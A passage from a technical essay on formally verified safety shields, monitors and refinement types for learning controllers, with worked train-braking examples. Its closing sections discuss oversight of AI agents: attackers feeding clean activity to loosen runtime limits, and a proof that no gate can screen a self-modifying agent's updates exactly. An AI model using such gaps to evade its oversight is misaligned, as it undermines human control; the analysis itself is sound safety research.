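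Computing the safe actions is the difficult part. *Adaptive Shielding via Parametric Safety Proofs* (Feng, Zhu and colleagues, 2025) explains that most shields find them by automatic search. Some search in advance and store the result for every state in a table, which becomes unmanageable for large systems. Others search while the system runs, and most of these look only a limited time ahead. A proof in differential dynamic logic avoids both problems because it produces a formula that holds for every speed and distance.

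### The train that must stop

Feng and colleagues illustrate the logic with a train that may travel no further than a point e. Its position is x, its speed is v and its acceleration is a. At least once every T seconds the controller chooses between braking at rate B and accelerating at rate A. The model is a hybrid program, so called because it combines a computer's separate steps with continuous motion:

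```
Init  = A > 0 ∧ B > 0 ∧ T > 0 ∧ x + v²/2B ≤ e
Ctrl  = (a := −B) ∪ (?(x + vT + AT²/2 + (v + AT)²/2B ≤ e) ; a := A)
Plant = t := 0 ; {x′ = v, v′ = a, t′ = 1 & t ≤ T ∧ v ≥ 0}
Safe  = x ≤ e
```

In `Ctrl`, the symbol ∪ means that either side may run, and the program leaves open which. The question mark is a test that discards any run in which the condition is false, so the train can accelerate only if the long inequality holds. This inequality is the guard. `Plant` describes the physics. Position changes at rate v and speed at rate a, for any length of time up to T, and the train does not roll backwards. The safety claim is:

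```
Init → [(Ctrl ; Plant)*] Safe
```

The star means "repeat any number of times", and the square brackets mean "after every possible run". A run may end at any moment of the motion, so this covers every moment, not just those when the controller makes a decision.

The proof uses x + v²/(2B) ≤ e as its invariant. A train that brakes at rate B from speed v takes v/B seconds to stop and averages v/2 while braking, so it travels v²/(2B). The invariant therefore means that the train would stop at or before e if it began full braking now.

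- The invariant implies safety, because v²/2B is never negative.
- Braking preserves it. The rate of change of x + v²/2B is v + v(−B)/B = 0, so every metre the train travels shortens its braking distance by a metre.
- Accelerating makes both terms grow, so the sum is largest at the end of the interval. After T seconds the train is at x + vT + AT²/2 and its speed is v + AT. If we put these values into the invariant, we get exactly the guard.

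Suppose v = 20 m/s, A = B = 1 m/s² and T = 1 s. The guard then requires a remaining distance of at least

```
20·1 + 1·1²/2 + (20 + 1)²/2 = 20 + 0.5 + 220.5 = 241 m
```

The braking distance at 20 m/s is only 200 m, so with between 200 and 241 m left the train is still safe but must brake. If it accelerated for one second with 240 m left, it would then have 219.5 m left and a speed of 21 m/s. Stopping from that speed takes 220.5 m, so the train would overrun e by one metre.

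### Any controller behind the guard

The symbol ∪ has the same function as the havoc oracle in containment verification. The proof covers every sequence of choices between braking and accelerating, whether a driver, a hand-written program or a neural network makes them. To apply the proof to a learned controller, an engineer has the system check the guard before each command. If the network outputs acceleration and the guard fails, the train brakes instead. Within this limit, the network can optimize for time, energy or comfort, which the proof does not address.

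The proof does not cover commands missing from the model, such as coasting. Feng and colleagues also give a model in which the controller can set any acceleration u between −B and A. If the train responds to commands exactly, the guard is the same formula with u in place of A. Coasting (u = 0) at 20 m/s then requires 220 m.

A train with a proved guard can still give a rough ride. For example, the two-option train might have 230 m left at 20 m/s and a controller that always requests acceleration. The guard condition fails six times in a row, so the train brakes from 20 to 14 m/s. It then has 128 m left and the guard requires only 127 m, so it speeds up again. A controller that had learned to account for the guard could drive far more smoothly.

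### Monitors extracted from proofs

Engineers can carry out such proofs in KeYmaera X, a theorem prover for differential dynamic logic. *Overview of Logical Foundations of Cyber-Physical Systems* (Platzer, 2019), written by the logic's inventor, reports that fewer than 2,000 lines of the prover's code have to be correct for its proofs to be sound. Researchers have also verified the logic's soundness in two other provers, Isabelle and Coq. However, KeYmaera X calls outside solvers for formulas about real numbers, and those solvers normally have to be correct too.

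A proof about a hybrid program is a proof about a model. Platzer remarks that renaming a file with a proof about a bouncing ball to `car.kyx` would not make any car safer. ModelPlex, a method built into KeYmaera X, connects the model to the machine by deriving two runtime checks from it:

- The controller monitor tests a proposed command. For the train, it accepts braking at any time and acceleration if the guard holds.
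- The model monitor tests whether the last movement fits the physics. If the train had speed v and acceleration a, then t seconds later its speed should be v + at and it should have travelled vt + at²/2.

To derive its runtime checks, ModelPlex starts from the condition that some run of the model leads from the old measurements to the new ones. It then uses proof steps to turn this condition into arithmetic that a computer can evaluate quickly. *Verified Runtime Validation for Partially Observable Hybrid Systems* (2018) restates the method's theorem that any system passing the check stays safe, and extends the method to systems whose sensors reveal only part of the state.

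According to Platzer, this is the main advance over Simplex, whose monitors had no such proof and checked only the controller. The model monitor can also detect a problem too late. Suppose the train starts braking from 20 m/s with 200 m left, and a second later its speed is 19.4 m/s instead of 19. The monitor detects that the brakes are weaker than in the model, but at 0.6 m/s² the train needs about 333 m in total to stop.

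A monitor can also raise an alarm when the system is safe. Platzer proves that a bouncing ball never rises above the height from which it fell, and he keeps the proof simple by assuming that the ball loses no speed when it bounces. A real ball does lose speed, so it violates the monitors at its first bounce, even though losing speed helps it stay below its starting height.

ModelPlex's formulas use exact real numbers, which no processor can handle in general. VeriPhy, a tool from 2018, solves this problem with a chain of proofs from the model to machine code. The last step uses CakeML, a compiler that has been proved correct. The resulting sandbox checks the untrusted controller's commands, corrects them where necessary and reports when the physical system departs from the model.

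### Learning inside the envelope

An engineer can train a controller without monitors and add them only at deployment. Platzer notes that the controller then operates in an environment different from the one it was trained in, because the monitors override some of its commands. The train that brakes for six seconds is an example. The engineer can instead keep the monitors active during training.

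Fulton and Platzer (2018), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Formal Methods*, developed this into an algorithm they call justified speculative control. Each step has three parts:

1. The model monitor compares the previous state, the last action and the current state.
2. If they fit the model, the learner chooses among the actions that the controller monitor accepts. If not, it may choose any action.
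3. The learner observes the result and updates itself.

One theorem establishes that the system stays safe during and after training if the environment always fits the model. It treats the learning algorithm as a black box, so it applies to a simple table of expected rewards as well as to a deep network.

The learner gets more freedom when the model turns out to be false, because the list of safe actions came from that model and staying on it may be a mistake. The theorem does not guarantee safety in this case. As a substitute, Fulton and Platzer converted the monitor's yes-or-no answer into a number that measures how far the system has strayed from the model, and used it as a reward signal to steer the learner back.

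Fulton and Platzer tried the method on a simple model of adaptive cruise control, which keeps a car at a distance from the one in front. Inside the modelled region, the learner found safe behaviour faster than it did without the monitors. This is plausible because a monitor rejects a bad action at once, while an ordinary learner has to crash and then work out which earlier decision caused it. Outside the region, the reward signal reduced the number of unsafe states. They call these experiments preliminary. Platzer also points out that a learner trained inside an envelope can come to rely on the monitor's interventions, and that it learns nothing about behaviour outside the envelope.

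### Collision avoidance for aircraft

The best-known application of KeYmaera X is ACAS X, a system that the US Federal Aviation Administration developed to warn pilots of an impending mid-air collision and advise them, for example, to climb or descend. Its designers computed this advice by optimising over a probabilistic model of encounters and stored the results in a large table. Platzer estimates that a hybrid program containing the table would have had about half a trillion cases.

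Jean-Baptiste Jeannin and colleagues therefore split the problem in a 2017 paper. They first ignored the table and determined, for each kind of advice, the relative positions and speeds from which a pilot who follows it will miss the other aircraft. They proved the resulting formulas for these safe regions correct in KeYmaera X, under stated assumptions about how the pilot responds and how the other aircraft flies. They then compared the table with the regions. This step needs no theorem proving because it only evaluates the formulas at particular points.

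The comparison revealed cases where the system's advice conflicted with the theorem. A conflict need not cause a collision, because the system keeps updating its advice and a later instruction may still separate the aircraft. The team extended the proof to cover these later instructions. Unlike the train's guard, these formulas were used to test a finished design, and the most useful result was a list of cases where the design failed the test.

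### Refinement types over streams

With ACAS X and the train, the proof is about a model in one language and the working controller is a program in another. Jeannin's group at the University of Michigan has since tried to put both into a single program by means of refinement types. Chen, Vargas de Mendonça and colleagues (2024), in *Synchronous Programming with Refinement Types*, present MARVeLus, an extension of the language Zélus. In synchronous languages like these, which engineers also use for avionics, each variable is a stream that has one value per tick of a clock. In simplified notation, a counter looks like this:

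```
x : (v : int | □(0 ≤ v)) = 0 fby x + 1
```

The operator `fby`, short for "followed by", gives the first value and then the rule for later ones, so the stream is 0, 1, 2 and so on. The symbol □ means "now and at every later tick". The compiler checks the type before the program runs, by induction over time. It uses an SMT solver to prove that 0 ≤ 0, and that 0 ≤ x + 1 whenever 0 ≤ x.

Chen and colleagues had to adapt the usual type safety theorem, because the type of a stream can change as the stream advances. For example, the stream −1, 0, 1, 2 has the type "negative now, non-negative from the next tick on". After one tick, the remaining stream starts with 0, so it no longer has this type. In their version of preservation, the value a program emits satisfies the part of the type about the present, and the rest of the program satisfies the part about the future.

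A water tank illustrates how a programmer finds the right type. Water leaves the tank at 0.1 litres per second and, when a valve is open, enters at 0.5. The level must stay between 1 and 19 litres. The controller acts every 0.1 seconds, opening the valve at 1.5 litres and closing it at 18.5. If the type contains only the limits, the check fails because the solver finds a state with 19 litres and an open valve, from which the level rises above the limit before the valve can close. The controller never reaches that state, but the type does not exclude it. The programmer therefore adds to the type that the level is at most 18.96 litres while the valve is open and at least 1.01 while it is closed. The check then succeeds because the level can change for one more 0.1-second step without crossing a limit. The train's invariant leaves room for its braking distance in the same way.

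For a test on hardware, the team programmed a small robot to follow another along an 8-metre track without hitting it. The program has 52 lines of executable code and 37 lines of type specifications, and the check took less than 1.3 seconds on a laptop. They ran ten trials in each of three scenarios and measured the gap at the end:

| Behaviour of the robot in front | Average gap | Smallest gap |
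|---|---|---|
| Brakes abruptly to a stop | 0.46 m | 0.34 m |
| Slows down but keeps moving | 1.01 m | 0.70 m |
| Stands still throughout | 0.48 m | 0.28 m |

The robots never collided in these trials, but the proof covers fewer situations than the trials do. In the verified program, the lead robot always drives at constant speed and then brakes as hard as it can. Chen and colleagues chose this as the worst case and argue that the follower will also cope with gentler behaviour. Their argument is reasonable, but the type checker did not prove it, and only the first trial scenario matches the verified one. The train model, in contrast, leaves choices open, and its proof covers all of them.

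MARVeLus lets a programmer pair a simulated quantity with a real sensor, but the compiler verifies only the simulated half, so the real half must also be taken on trust. The real robots moved somewhat differently from the simulated ones, probably because of timing, starting conditions and physical details that the model left out. The braking rule includes an extra half-metre, which probably absorbed some of these differences. MARVeLus has no counterpart to ModelPlex's model monitor, so a running program cannot detect that its assumptions have failed.

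The types also simplify time by describing values at each tick and not the motion in between. *Verifiably Safe Exploration for End-to-End Reinforcement Learning* (2020), which takes its guards from differential dynamic logic, requires that a vehicle avoid an obstacle at every point of its continuous path. Dane, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Formal Verification of Hybrid Synchronous Programs with Refinement Types*, bring reasoning about continuous motion into the type system. Their programs contain differential equations, and the controller acts when a chosen quantity rises through zero.

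In one example, a vehicle starts at position 0 with speed 1 and accelerates at a rate of 1 towards an obstacle at position 5. It can brake at a rate of 0.2, so its braking distance at speed v is v²/0.4. Braking starts when the vehicle's position plus its braking distance plus a margin of 0.1 reaches the obstacle's position. This happens at position 0.4, where the braking distance is 4.5, so the vehicle stops at 4.9.

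"Rises through zero" is hard to define because a function can touch zero, stay there for a while or oscillate around it. Dane and colleagues distinguish 85 cases. The distinctions matter in the braking example. During full braking, the sum of position and braking distance is constant, as it was for the train, so the trigger stays at exactly zero and cannot fire again. The rest of the proof therefore has to rely on the differential equation.

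The team proved the extended type system sound and verified the examples by hand. Their controllers react at the exact instant of the crossing, whereas a real computer checks at intervals. T represents this delay in the train model.

Writing the types can be useful in itself. Fonseca reports finding four bugs in a drone controller just by writing its specification. His group also used refinement types to detect 84 real configuration errors in robots that use ROS, a common software framework.

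### What the envelope costs

All these proofs assume a correct world model. If the train's brakes deliver 0.8 m/s² instead of 1, it needs 250 m to stop from 20 m/s, but the invariant guarantees only 200 m. Engineers can guard against this by assuming the worst case, but setting B to 0.5 m/s² to allow for wet rails raises the distance required for accelerating at 20 m/s from 241 m to 461.5 m, even when the rails are dry. Slower decisions also increase the required distance. With the original braking value, a controller that decides only every two seconds needs 284 m instead of 241 m. Shields that update their model from measurements can remove some of this extra distance.

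A safe fallback must also exist at every moment, because the monitor cannot create a safe action if none is physically possible. The train can always brake, and a stationary train is safe, at least if nothing is coming up behind it. An aircraft cannot stop in mid-air, so it needs a different fallback. Fulton and Platzer's algorithm assumes that the controller monitor always accepts at least one action, and Chen and colleagues note that VeriPhy likewise needs a safe controller to switch to.

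Changing the design also takes a lot of work, since each new version needs a new proof, often one much like the last. *Refactoring-as-Propositions* (2026) reduces this work by proving common design changes correct once, in a form that engineers can reuse for other systems. The method relates one hybrid program to another, much as containment verification relates an implementation to its specification.

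## Learning and adaptation within proved bounds

Proving every new version safe is too slow for an agent that learns while it works. Engineers can instead prove in advance that a set of changes is safe, then let the agent or its developers make any change in that set. In some systems, the controller keeps learning behind a fixed shield. In others, a developer replaces a component with one whose type is a subtype of the original's. The most ambitious designs loosen the shield as measurements arrive.

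### Bounded adaptation

These are all forms of bounded adaptation, if the term means change restricted to a set of changes already proved safe. The idea fits into a refinement type:

```
adapt : (c : Config | safe(c)) → Evidence → (d : Config | safe(d))
```

`Config` covers whatever can change, such as network weights, thresholds or the choice of components. Evidence can influence which configuration comes next, but the next configuration is always safe.

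Other researchers use the term "bounded adaptation" with weaker guarantees. *When Intelligence Becomes Agency* (2026), a theory of governed AI agents, defines it as learning that changes an agent's state and learned parameters only within an "admissible update relation", but does not require a proof that the admissible updates are safe. In *Guardrailed Meta-Agent Loops* (2026), people fix the goal, budget and scope of a series of experiments, and the system may change only its learning configuration. It picks changes from a catalogue, and ordinary code defines what each entry does, so people can inspect every entry in advance. The paper tests this design in a simulator but gives no proof.

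### Learning behind an unchanged shield

Fulton and Platzer's theorem already covers this case, so nobody has to check an update to a controller that learns behind a fixed shield.

*Mimir* (2026) applies the same division to a language-model agent that controls irrigation. The system makes an update only when the agent needs the same correction or triggers the same safeguard often enough. It then draws a short principle from the records and adds it to the model's context. These principles cannot relax a safety bound, change the scoring rule or bypass the fixed procedure that selects the final action. A bad principle can still lead to poor irrigation, but only within the existing bounds.

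The drawback is that the shield cannot use anything the agent learns, so a train whose shield allows for wet rails keeps the longer distance even after years of dry rails.

### Replacing a component

Suppose a component reads a temperature between 0 and 100 degrees and sets a cooling valve to a position between 0 and 10. An engineer wants to replace it with one that accepts temperatures up to 200 and never opens the valve beyond 5:

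```
old : (x : int | 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 100) → (v : int | 0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 10)
new : (x : int | 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 200) → (v : int | 0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 5)
```

The type of `new` is a subtype of the type of `old`, so the checker accepts the replacement once it has proved two implications:

```
inputs:   ∀x. (0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 100)  ⇒  (0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 200)
results:  ∀v. (0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 5)    ⇒  (0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 10)
```

The reverse, replacing `new` with `old`, fails for both the input and the result. A program written for `new` may pass in a temperature of 150, which `old` does not accept. It may also rely on a result of at most 5, but `old` can return 8.

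The permitted result can depend on the input. For example, a component might accept temperatures up to 200 and return at most a tenth of the temperature. It may return 20 when given 200, but it can still replace `old` because the surrounding program never passes in more than 100 and so never gets back more than 10.

The rest of the program needs no new check, since its proof used only the type of `old`. This makes the rule useful for learned components. If an engineer wraps a network in code that clamps its results to between 0 and 10, the wrapped component has the required result type whatever the network's weights are. The engineer can retrain the network every night and install the new version without another proof.

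However, the type protects only the property it states. Both types above prevent the valve from opening too far. If the machine needs the valve at 8 or more from 90 degrees upwards, `new` is dangerous, because it never goes beyond 5. The checker would even accept a component that always keeps the valve shut. To prevent this, the engineer has to include the requirement in the type of `old`:

```
old : (x : int | 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 100) → (v : int | 0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 10 ∧ (x ≥ 90 ⇒ v ≥ 8))
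```

The solver now finds the counterexample x = 95, v = 5, and the checker rejects the replacement.

*When Intelligence Becomes Agency* proposes a similar rule for agents that delegate work. A sub-agent's permissions must lie within those of the agent that appointed it, so authority can shrink along the chain but not grow. If several parties impose hard limits, the agent may do only what all of them allow. For example, if one party sets a spending limit of 100 and another sets a limit of 60, the agent may spend at most 60.

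### A shield with unknowns in it

Subtyping and fixed shields keep the original limits, while the adaptive shields of Feng and colleagues can give an agent more freedom than it had at the start. An engineer writes the safety model with symbols for unknown quantities, and the system narrows their possible values as it runs.

In one of their examples, a train does not respond exactly to commands. If the controller requests an acceleration u, the actual acceleration is:

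```
v′ = θu + φ
```

Here θ describes how strongly the train responds, and φ is a constant disturbance. Both are unknown, but the shield has a lower bound θ_low and an upper bound θ_high for θ, and an upper bound φ_high for φ. Under full braking the command is −B, so the train slows at a rate of θB − φ, which is at least θ_low·B − φ_high. This guaranteed rate takes the place of B in the train's invariant:

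```
x + v² / (2·(θ_low·B − φ_high)) ≤ e
```

Suppose B is 1 m/s² and the engineer starts with θ_low = 0.7 and φ_high = 0.2. The guaranteed braking rate is then 0.5 m/s², and the stopping distance from 20 m/s is:

```
20² / (2·0.5) = 400 m
```

Measurements later raise θ_low to 0.95 and lower φ_high to 0.05. The guaranteed rate rises to 0.9 m/s², and the distance falls to:

```
20² / (2·0.9) ≈ 222 m
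```

Only the shield's estimate of the train's brakes has changed. The bound θ_high also matters because it limits how much speed the train can gain before the next decision. If decisions come once a second and θ_high falls from 1.1 to 1.05 in the same period, the distance required for a command to accelerate at 1 m/s² drops from about 474 m to 268 m.

The engineer proves the invariant once with symbolic bounds, so the proof covers every value the bounds can take. While the train runs, the shield only has to insert their current values.

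Feng and colleagues also require that tighter bounds only enlarge the set of states the shield classifies as safe. Without this condition, a new bound could leave the train in a position from which no action is provably safe. For example, a train at 20 m/s with 300 m left is safe at a guaranteed braking rate of 0.9 m/s². If the shield went back to 0.5 m/s², its model would give the same train a stopping distance of 400 m, more than it has left. The shield therefore replaces a bound only when the new one is tighter.

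This works because θ and φ are constants in the model. If it starts to rain after the shield has settled on 0.9 m/s², the true braking rate may fall below the guaranteed one, and the theorem no longer applies. An engineer who expects rain has to include it in the model from the start.

### Bounds that hold only nearby

Some quantities vary from place to place. In another version of the train model, the track has an unknown slope, which adds f(x) to the train's acceleration at position x. The engineer assumes that this effect is at most F and changes by at most k per metre.

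Suppose the brakes deliver 4 m/s², F is 3 m/s² and k is 0.0025 m/s² per metre. In the worst case only 1 m/s² of braking is left, so a train at 30 m/s needs 450 m to stop. Now suppose the shield has established that the slope adds at most 0.5 m/s² at the train's current position. The shield can then improve its estimate in three steps:

1. Even in the worst case the train stops within 450 m, so only the slope on that stretch matters.
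2. Over 450 m, the effect can grow by at most 0.0025 × 450 = 1.125 m/s², to 1.625 m/s².
3. The train therefore brakes at 2.375 m/s² or more and stops within about 190 m.

The local bound weakens as the train moves. At 30 m/s, it rises by 0.075 m/s² every second until the shield obtains a new bound. The invariant accounts for this increase, so the train stays safe even if no further measurement arrives.

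### From noisy measurements to bounds

Measurements contain errors, so a bound derived from them can be false. Feng and colleagues designed a small language in which an engineer describes how the shield may compute its bounds. For the slope, the description has three lines, slightly simplified here:

```
f_high := F
f_high := BEST i : f_high(i) + k·|x − x(i)|
f_high := AGGREGATE i : ω(i) + k·|x − x(i)|  AND  η(i)
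```

The first line allows the general maximum at any time. The second carries an earlier bound over to the current position, adding k for every metre in between. The third uses raw measurements, where ω(i) is the i-th reading and η(i) is its unknown error.

Each line produces a formula that the engineer must prove. For the third it is:

```
|f(x) − f(x(i))| ≤ k·|x − x(i)|  ∧  ω(i) = f(x(i)) − η(i)
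    ⇒  f(x) ≤ ω(i) + k·|x − x(i)| + η(i)
```

This is ordinary algebra, without probabilities. A general theorem about the language then replaces the unknown error with a margin large enough for the chosen risk. If the errors are normally distributed with standard deviation 0.1 m/s² and the engineer accepts a risk of 10⁻⁷, a single reading needs a margin of about 0.52 m/s². The average of 25 independent readings needs only 0.10 m/s². However, averaging includes readings from further back, and one taken 200 m ago could be off by a further 0.5 m/s² because the slope may have changed since.

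A learned component can decide how to weigh the readings and how much risk to allot to each estimate. A poor decision makes the shield too cautious but cannot invalidate the proof. A fixed rule that used every reading at once had a return (total reward per run) of 9.6 on irregular tracks with accurate sensors and 6.4 on smooth tracks with noisy sensors. The learned component had a return of 9.1 in both settings.

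The only thing this component may not do is choose readings by their values. If each reading has a 1 per cent chance of giving a false bound, an agent that takes 100 readings has a 63 per cent chance of getting at least one false bound, and keeping the most favourable reading would select exactly such a bound. Selecting experimental results this way is called p-hacking. The shield therefore hides the values and reveals only where and when readings are available. It also uses each reading in only one decision cycle, because the agent's later position may depend on an earlier reading's value, so choosing that reading by position would amount to choosing it by value.

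Besides the formulas for the inference lines, the engineer has to prove four things about the shield:

- The invariant and the bounds together imply safety.
- Every permitted action preserves the invariant.
- At least one permitted action always exists.
- Tighter bounds never make the invariant harder to satisfy.

The four case studies produced 32 proof obligations. KeYmaera X proved 27 of them automatically or with trivial help, and an experienced user can prove each of the others in under an hour.

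### The theorem and the safety budget

The main theorem starts with a safety budget ε, the total probability of failure that the engineer accepts. If the environment fits the model and the initial state satisfies the invariant and the bounds, the entire run is safe with probability at least 1 − ε, whatever learning algorithm is used.

Each estimate the shield makes has some risk of being false, written ε₁, ε₂ and so on. The probability that at least one estimate is false is at most the sum of these risks, and the shield skips any estimate that would take the sum above a budget ε. If all the estimates are true, the proof in differential dynamic logic applies and the system is safe at every moment. When the budget runs out, the shield stops making estimates from new readings but continues to protect the agent, so the total risk stays at or below ε however long the run lasts.

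It does grow with the number of runs if each has its own budget. In one case study a train practised on about 6,000 randomly generated tracks, with a budget of 10⁻⁷ for each. The probability of any failure in training was therefore at most:

```
6,000 × 10⁻⁷ = 6 × 10⁻⁴
```

The same arithmetic applies to a fleet. A railway with 1,000 journeys a day and a budget of 10⁻⁷ per journey could guarantee only that the risk of a failure stays below about 3.7 per cent a year. An engineer therefore has to account for the whole period of use when choosing the budget.

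### Results in simulation

Feng and colleagues trained agents with an adaptive shield, with a shield whose bounds never changed, and with no shield. All of them received the same estimates as information, so the main difference was whether the shield used them. The returns below come from tests after training, averaged over three runs:

| Case study | Return, no shield | Return, fixed shield | Return, adaptive shield | Crashes in training, no shield |
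|---|---|---|---|---|
| Train on one hilly line | 8.3 | 5.5 | 7.0 | 110.7 |
| Train on changing tracks, irregular slope and accurate sensors | 10.0 | 5.8 | 9.1 | 102.7 |
| Train on changing tracks, smooth slope and noisy sensors | 9.5 | 5.8 | 9.1 | 94.3 |
| Robot crossing a river | 3.9 | −5.0 | 4.2 | 325.7 |
| Aircraft avoiding another aircraft | 6.7 | 4.5 | 6.6 | 987.0 |

No shielded agent crashed in training or testing. The unshielded aircraft still crashed 25 times on average during the tests. For the trains and the aircraft, adaptation recovered between 54 and 95 per cent of the return lost under the fixed shield.

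The robot depends on adaptation most. It has to cross a river at night over a bridge whose position it does not know, and its lamp lights only a small area. With a fixed shield it can never be certain enough to cross, so it wanders until time runs out and loses exactly 5 points. With the adaptive shield it learned to walk to the river, switch on the lamp and follow the bank until it found the bridge.

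In the aircraft study, a gentler manoeuvre is enough if the other plane is following the standard rules for avoiding collisions, but it may not be. The agent gets two independent pieces of evidence, one from radio calls and one from the other plane's flight path. Each wrongly indicates a rule-following plane with a probability of 10⁻⁴, which exceeds the allowed 10⁻⁷. The probability that both are wrong is 10⁻⁸, so the shield relaxes only if both indicate that the plane is following the rules.

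The absence of crashes is weak evidence for a risk as small as 10⁻⁷, so confidence in that figure has to come from the proof. Even 18,000 safe episodes can rule out only failure rates above roughly 1 in 6,000, with 95 per cent confidence. The team also tested larger budgets, which allow a better comparison between the theorem and practice. On smooth tracks with noisy sensors, training led to an average of 124 crashes with a budget of 0.1 per episode and 0.3 with a budget of 0.001. The theorem's limits were about 600 and 6 crashes, or about 4.8 and 20 times the observed averages.

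### When the assumptions fail

The shield's guarantee depends heavily on an assumption about sensor error, which held exactly in simulation but may not hold for real sensors. For normally distributed errors, a risk of 10⁻⁶ requires a margin of 4.75 standard deviations. If the engineer knows the standard deviation but not the shape of the distribution, Chebyshev's inequality still gives a valid margin, but it is about 1,000 standard deviations. On the hilly line, where errors stayed within known limits, the team compared this inequality with Hoeffding's, which uses those limits. The agent earned 7.0 with Hoeffding's and 5.4 with Chebyshev's, which is no better than the fixed shield's 5.5.

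Averaging reduces random errors but not systematic ones, so more readings from a faulty sensor only narrow the confidence interval around a wrong value. Suppose such a sensor leads the shield to use a guaranteed braking rate of 0.9 m/s² when the true rate is 0.7 m/s². At 20 m/s, the shield lets the train come within 222 m of the stopping point before braking, but the train needs 286 m to stop, so it overruns by about 64 m.

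The assumed form of the unknowns matters just as much. The slope model fails if the track has a sudden step, and the response model fails if the brakes fade as they heat up, because θ is then no longer constant. A fixed shield with generous worst-case bounds can tolerate some of these errors, but an adaptive shield gradually loses that margin. Like MARVeLus, the adaptive shield has no model monitor that could report the mismatch.

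These assumptions are at least explicit, and an engineer can check a limit on slope against a survey of the track. Feng and colleagues contrast this with shields based on Gaussian processes, a statistical method for learning an unknown function from data. Those shields rely on assumptions about the function's smoothness that are implicit in the choice of kernel, and the team considers them nearly impossible to test by experiment.

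### Shields that learn the model itself

Several groups have nevertheless let the shield learn how the system moves. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Recovery-based Shielding with Gaussian Process Dynamics Models* (2026) does this with a Gaussian process and a backup controller that can return the system to a verified safe region. On the standard task of balancing a pole on a cart, its theorem guaranteed safety with a probability of 0.98, and measured safety was 1.00. On a harder version of the task, the agent again stayed safe but earned a return of only 30.7. Constrained policy optimisation, an unshielded method that limits the expected amount of unsafe behaviour, earned 152.0 with a measured safety of 0.98. In another task, the shield intervened at every step, so the backup controller chose every action. The paper concludes that performance depends critically on the backup controller and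 on the size of the verified region.

Learned models also make it harder to guarantee that a safe action exists. In *Adaptive Shielding for Safe Reinforcement Learning under Hidden-Parameter Dynamics Shifts* (2025), the shield looks for an action that makes the next state safe with probability above 1 − δ. If it finds none, it samples several actions and takes the one with the best predicted safety margin, which may still be unsafe. The guarantee also covers only one step at a time. With δ at 1 per cent, the risks can add up to 100 per cent after 100 steps, whereas Feng and colleagues' budget covers the entire run.

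*Adaptive Probabilistic Shielding by Learning MDPs for Safe Reinforcement Learning* (Brorholt, Galesloot and colleagues, 2026) assumes that the engineer knows which states can follow each action but not how likely each one is. Its shield estimates a range for each probability from the agent's experience. Suppose an action leads to an accident with a probability between 10 and 30 per cent, and the limit is 20 per cent. A robust shield uses the 30 per cent figure and blocks the action, while an optimistic one uses 10 per cent and allows it. Under the robust shield, the agent may never collect the data that would show the action to be acceptable, whereas the optimistic shield lets it collect that data but exposes it to risk in the meantime.

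Collecting such data can involve many accidents. If the true risk of an accident is 15 per cent, the standard statistical bound requires roughly 1,500 trials to show with 99.9 per cent confidence that the risk is below 20 per cent, and around 230 of those trials would end in an accident. That is acceptable in a simulator, which Brorholt and colleagues assume is available, but not on a railway. A train can collect data on its brakes without crashing, because every ordinary braking manoeuvre provides a measurement.

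Permitting a small risk also creates a problem that more data cannot solve. Heck, Macák and colleagues (2026), in *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs*, prove that no shield can both keep the risk within a limit in every case and never interfere with a safe controller. In their counterexample, a coin toss sends an agent into one of two rooms, each with a safe door and a door that always leads to an accident, and the limit is a risk of 50 per cent. A controller that takes the dangerous door in only one of the rooms stays within the limit, but one that takes it in both always has an accident. The shield observes only the room the agent has entered, so if it never interferes with controllers that take the dangerous door in one room, it cannot stop the controller that takes it in both.

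A designer therefore has to decide which of the safe controllers to allow. Heck and colleagues build shields that start strict and permit more as they process records of the agent's behaviour, without ever exceeding the limit. However, a permissive shield can require very large records. Feng and colleagues avoid the conflict differently, with a shield that permits no risk as long as its bounds are true. The allowed risk covers only the chance that a bound is false.

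### Evidence that an attacker can influence

In *Governing What You Cannot Observe*, Marín and Chaudhary (2026) recommend a control system for AI agents that work with software and money. Each stage can restrict what earlier stages decided but can never relax it, and the component that adjusts limits while the agent runs may only tighten them or stop the agent. They rule out loosening because an attacker could otherwise feed the system harmless-looking activity until it raised its thresholds. They have not yet evaluated the design quantitatively, and a series of false alarms could restrict a useful agent until it can do hardly anything.

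The two designs rest on different kinds of evidence. An engineer can measure the errors in a train's acceleration readings in advance, and nobody gains by distorting the readings. But a payment agent or an attacker can deliberately produce a clean payment record. An agent might make a hundred correct small payments because it is reliable, or because someone wants its limit raised before the next one. No error distribution covers the second case, so a budget like that of Feng and colleagues would not bound the risk. A company can still raise the limit, but it would be relying on its own judgement rather than the theorem.

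## Agents that modify themselves

The adaptive systems described so far change only what an engineer chose in advance, and the agent never modifies the shield or the checker. A self-modifying agent can propose new versions of its own code, its goals or even the checker that approves its proposals. The checker then has to judge programs that nobody foresaw, and there are mathematical limits to how well any automatic checker can do this.

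### No gate accepts exactly the improvements

Moser, Frolov and colleagues (2026), in *The Self-Improvement Problem*, treat the current agent p, the proposed version q and the gate V as programs. V reads p and q, always finishes, and returns 1 to accept the update or 0 to reject it. The proof uses a simple score J, where J(p) is 1 if p outputs 1 on the input 0, and 0 if p outputs anything else or runs forever. An update is a genuine improvement if J(q) > J(p).

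An ideal gate would be sound, accepting only genuine improvements, and complete, accepting all of them. Suppose someone has built one. Let p be a program that outputs 0, so J(p) = 0, and let q be this program:

```
q(0) = if V(p, q) = 1 then 0 else 1
```

The program q runs the gate on itself and then makes the verdict wrong:

- If the gate accepts q, then q outputs 0 and J(q) = 0. The gate has accepted an update that is no improvement.
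- If the gate rejects q, then q outputs 1 and J(q) = 1. The gate has rejected a genuine improvement.

The ideal gate therefore cannot exist. Kleene's recursion theorem guarantees that q exists even though its definition refers to q itself. A quine, which prints its own source code, is a simple example of a self-referential program. The proof also requires a gate that always finishes, because otherwise q might wait forever for the verdict.

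The argument extends beyond the simple score to any score that depends only on a program's behaviour and takes at least two values, one better than the other. The candidate then behaves badly if the gate accepts it and well if the gate rejects it.

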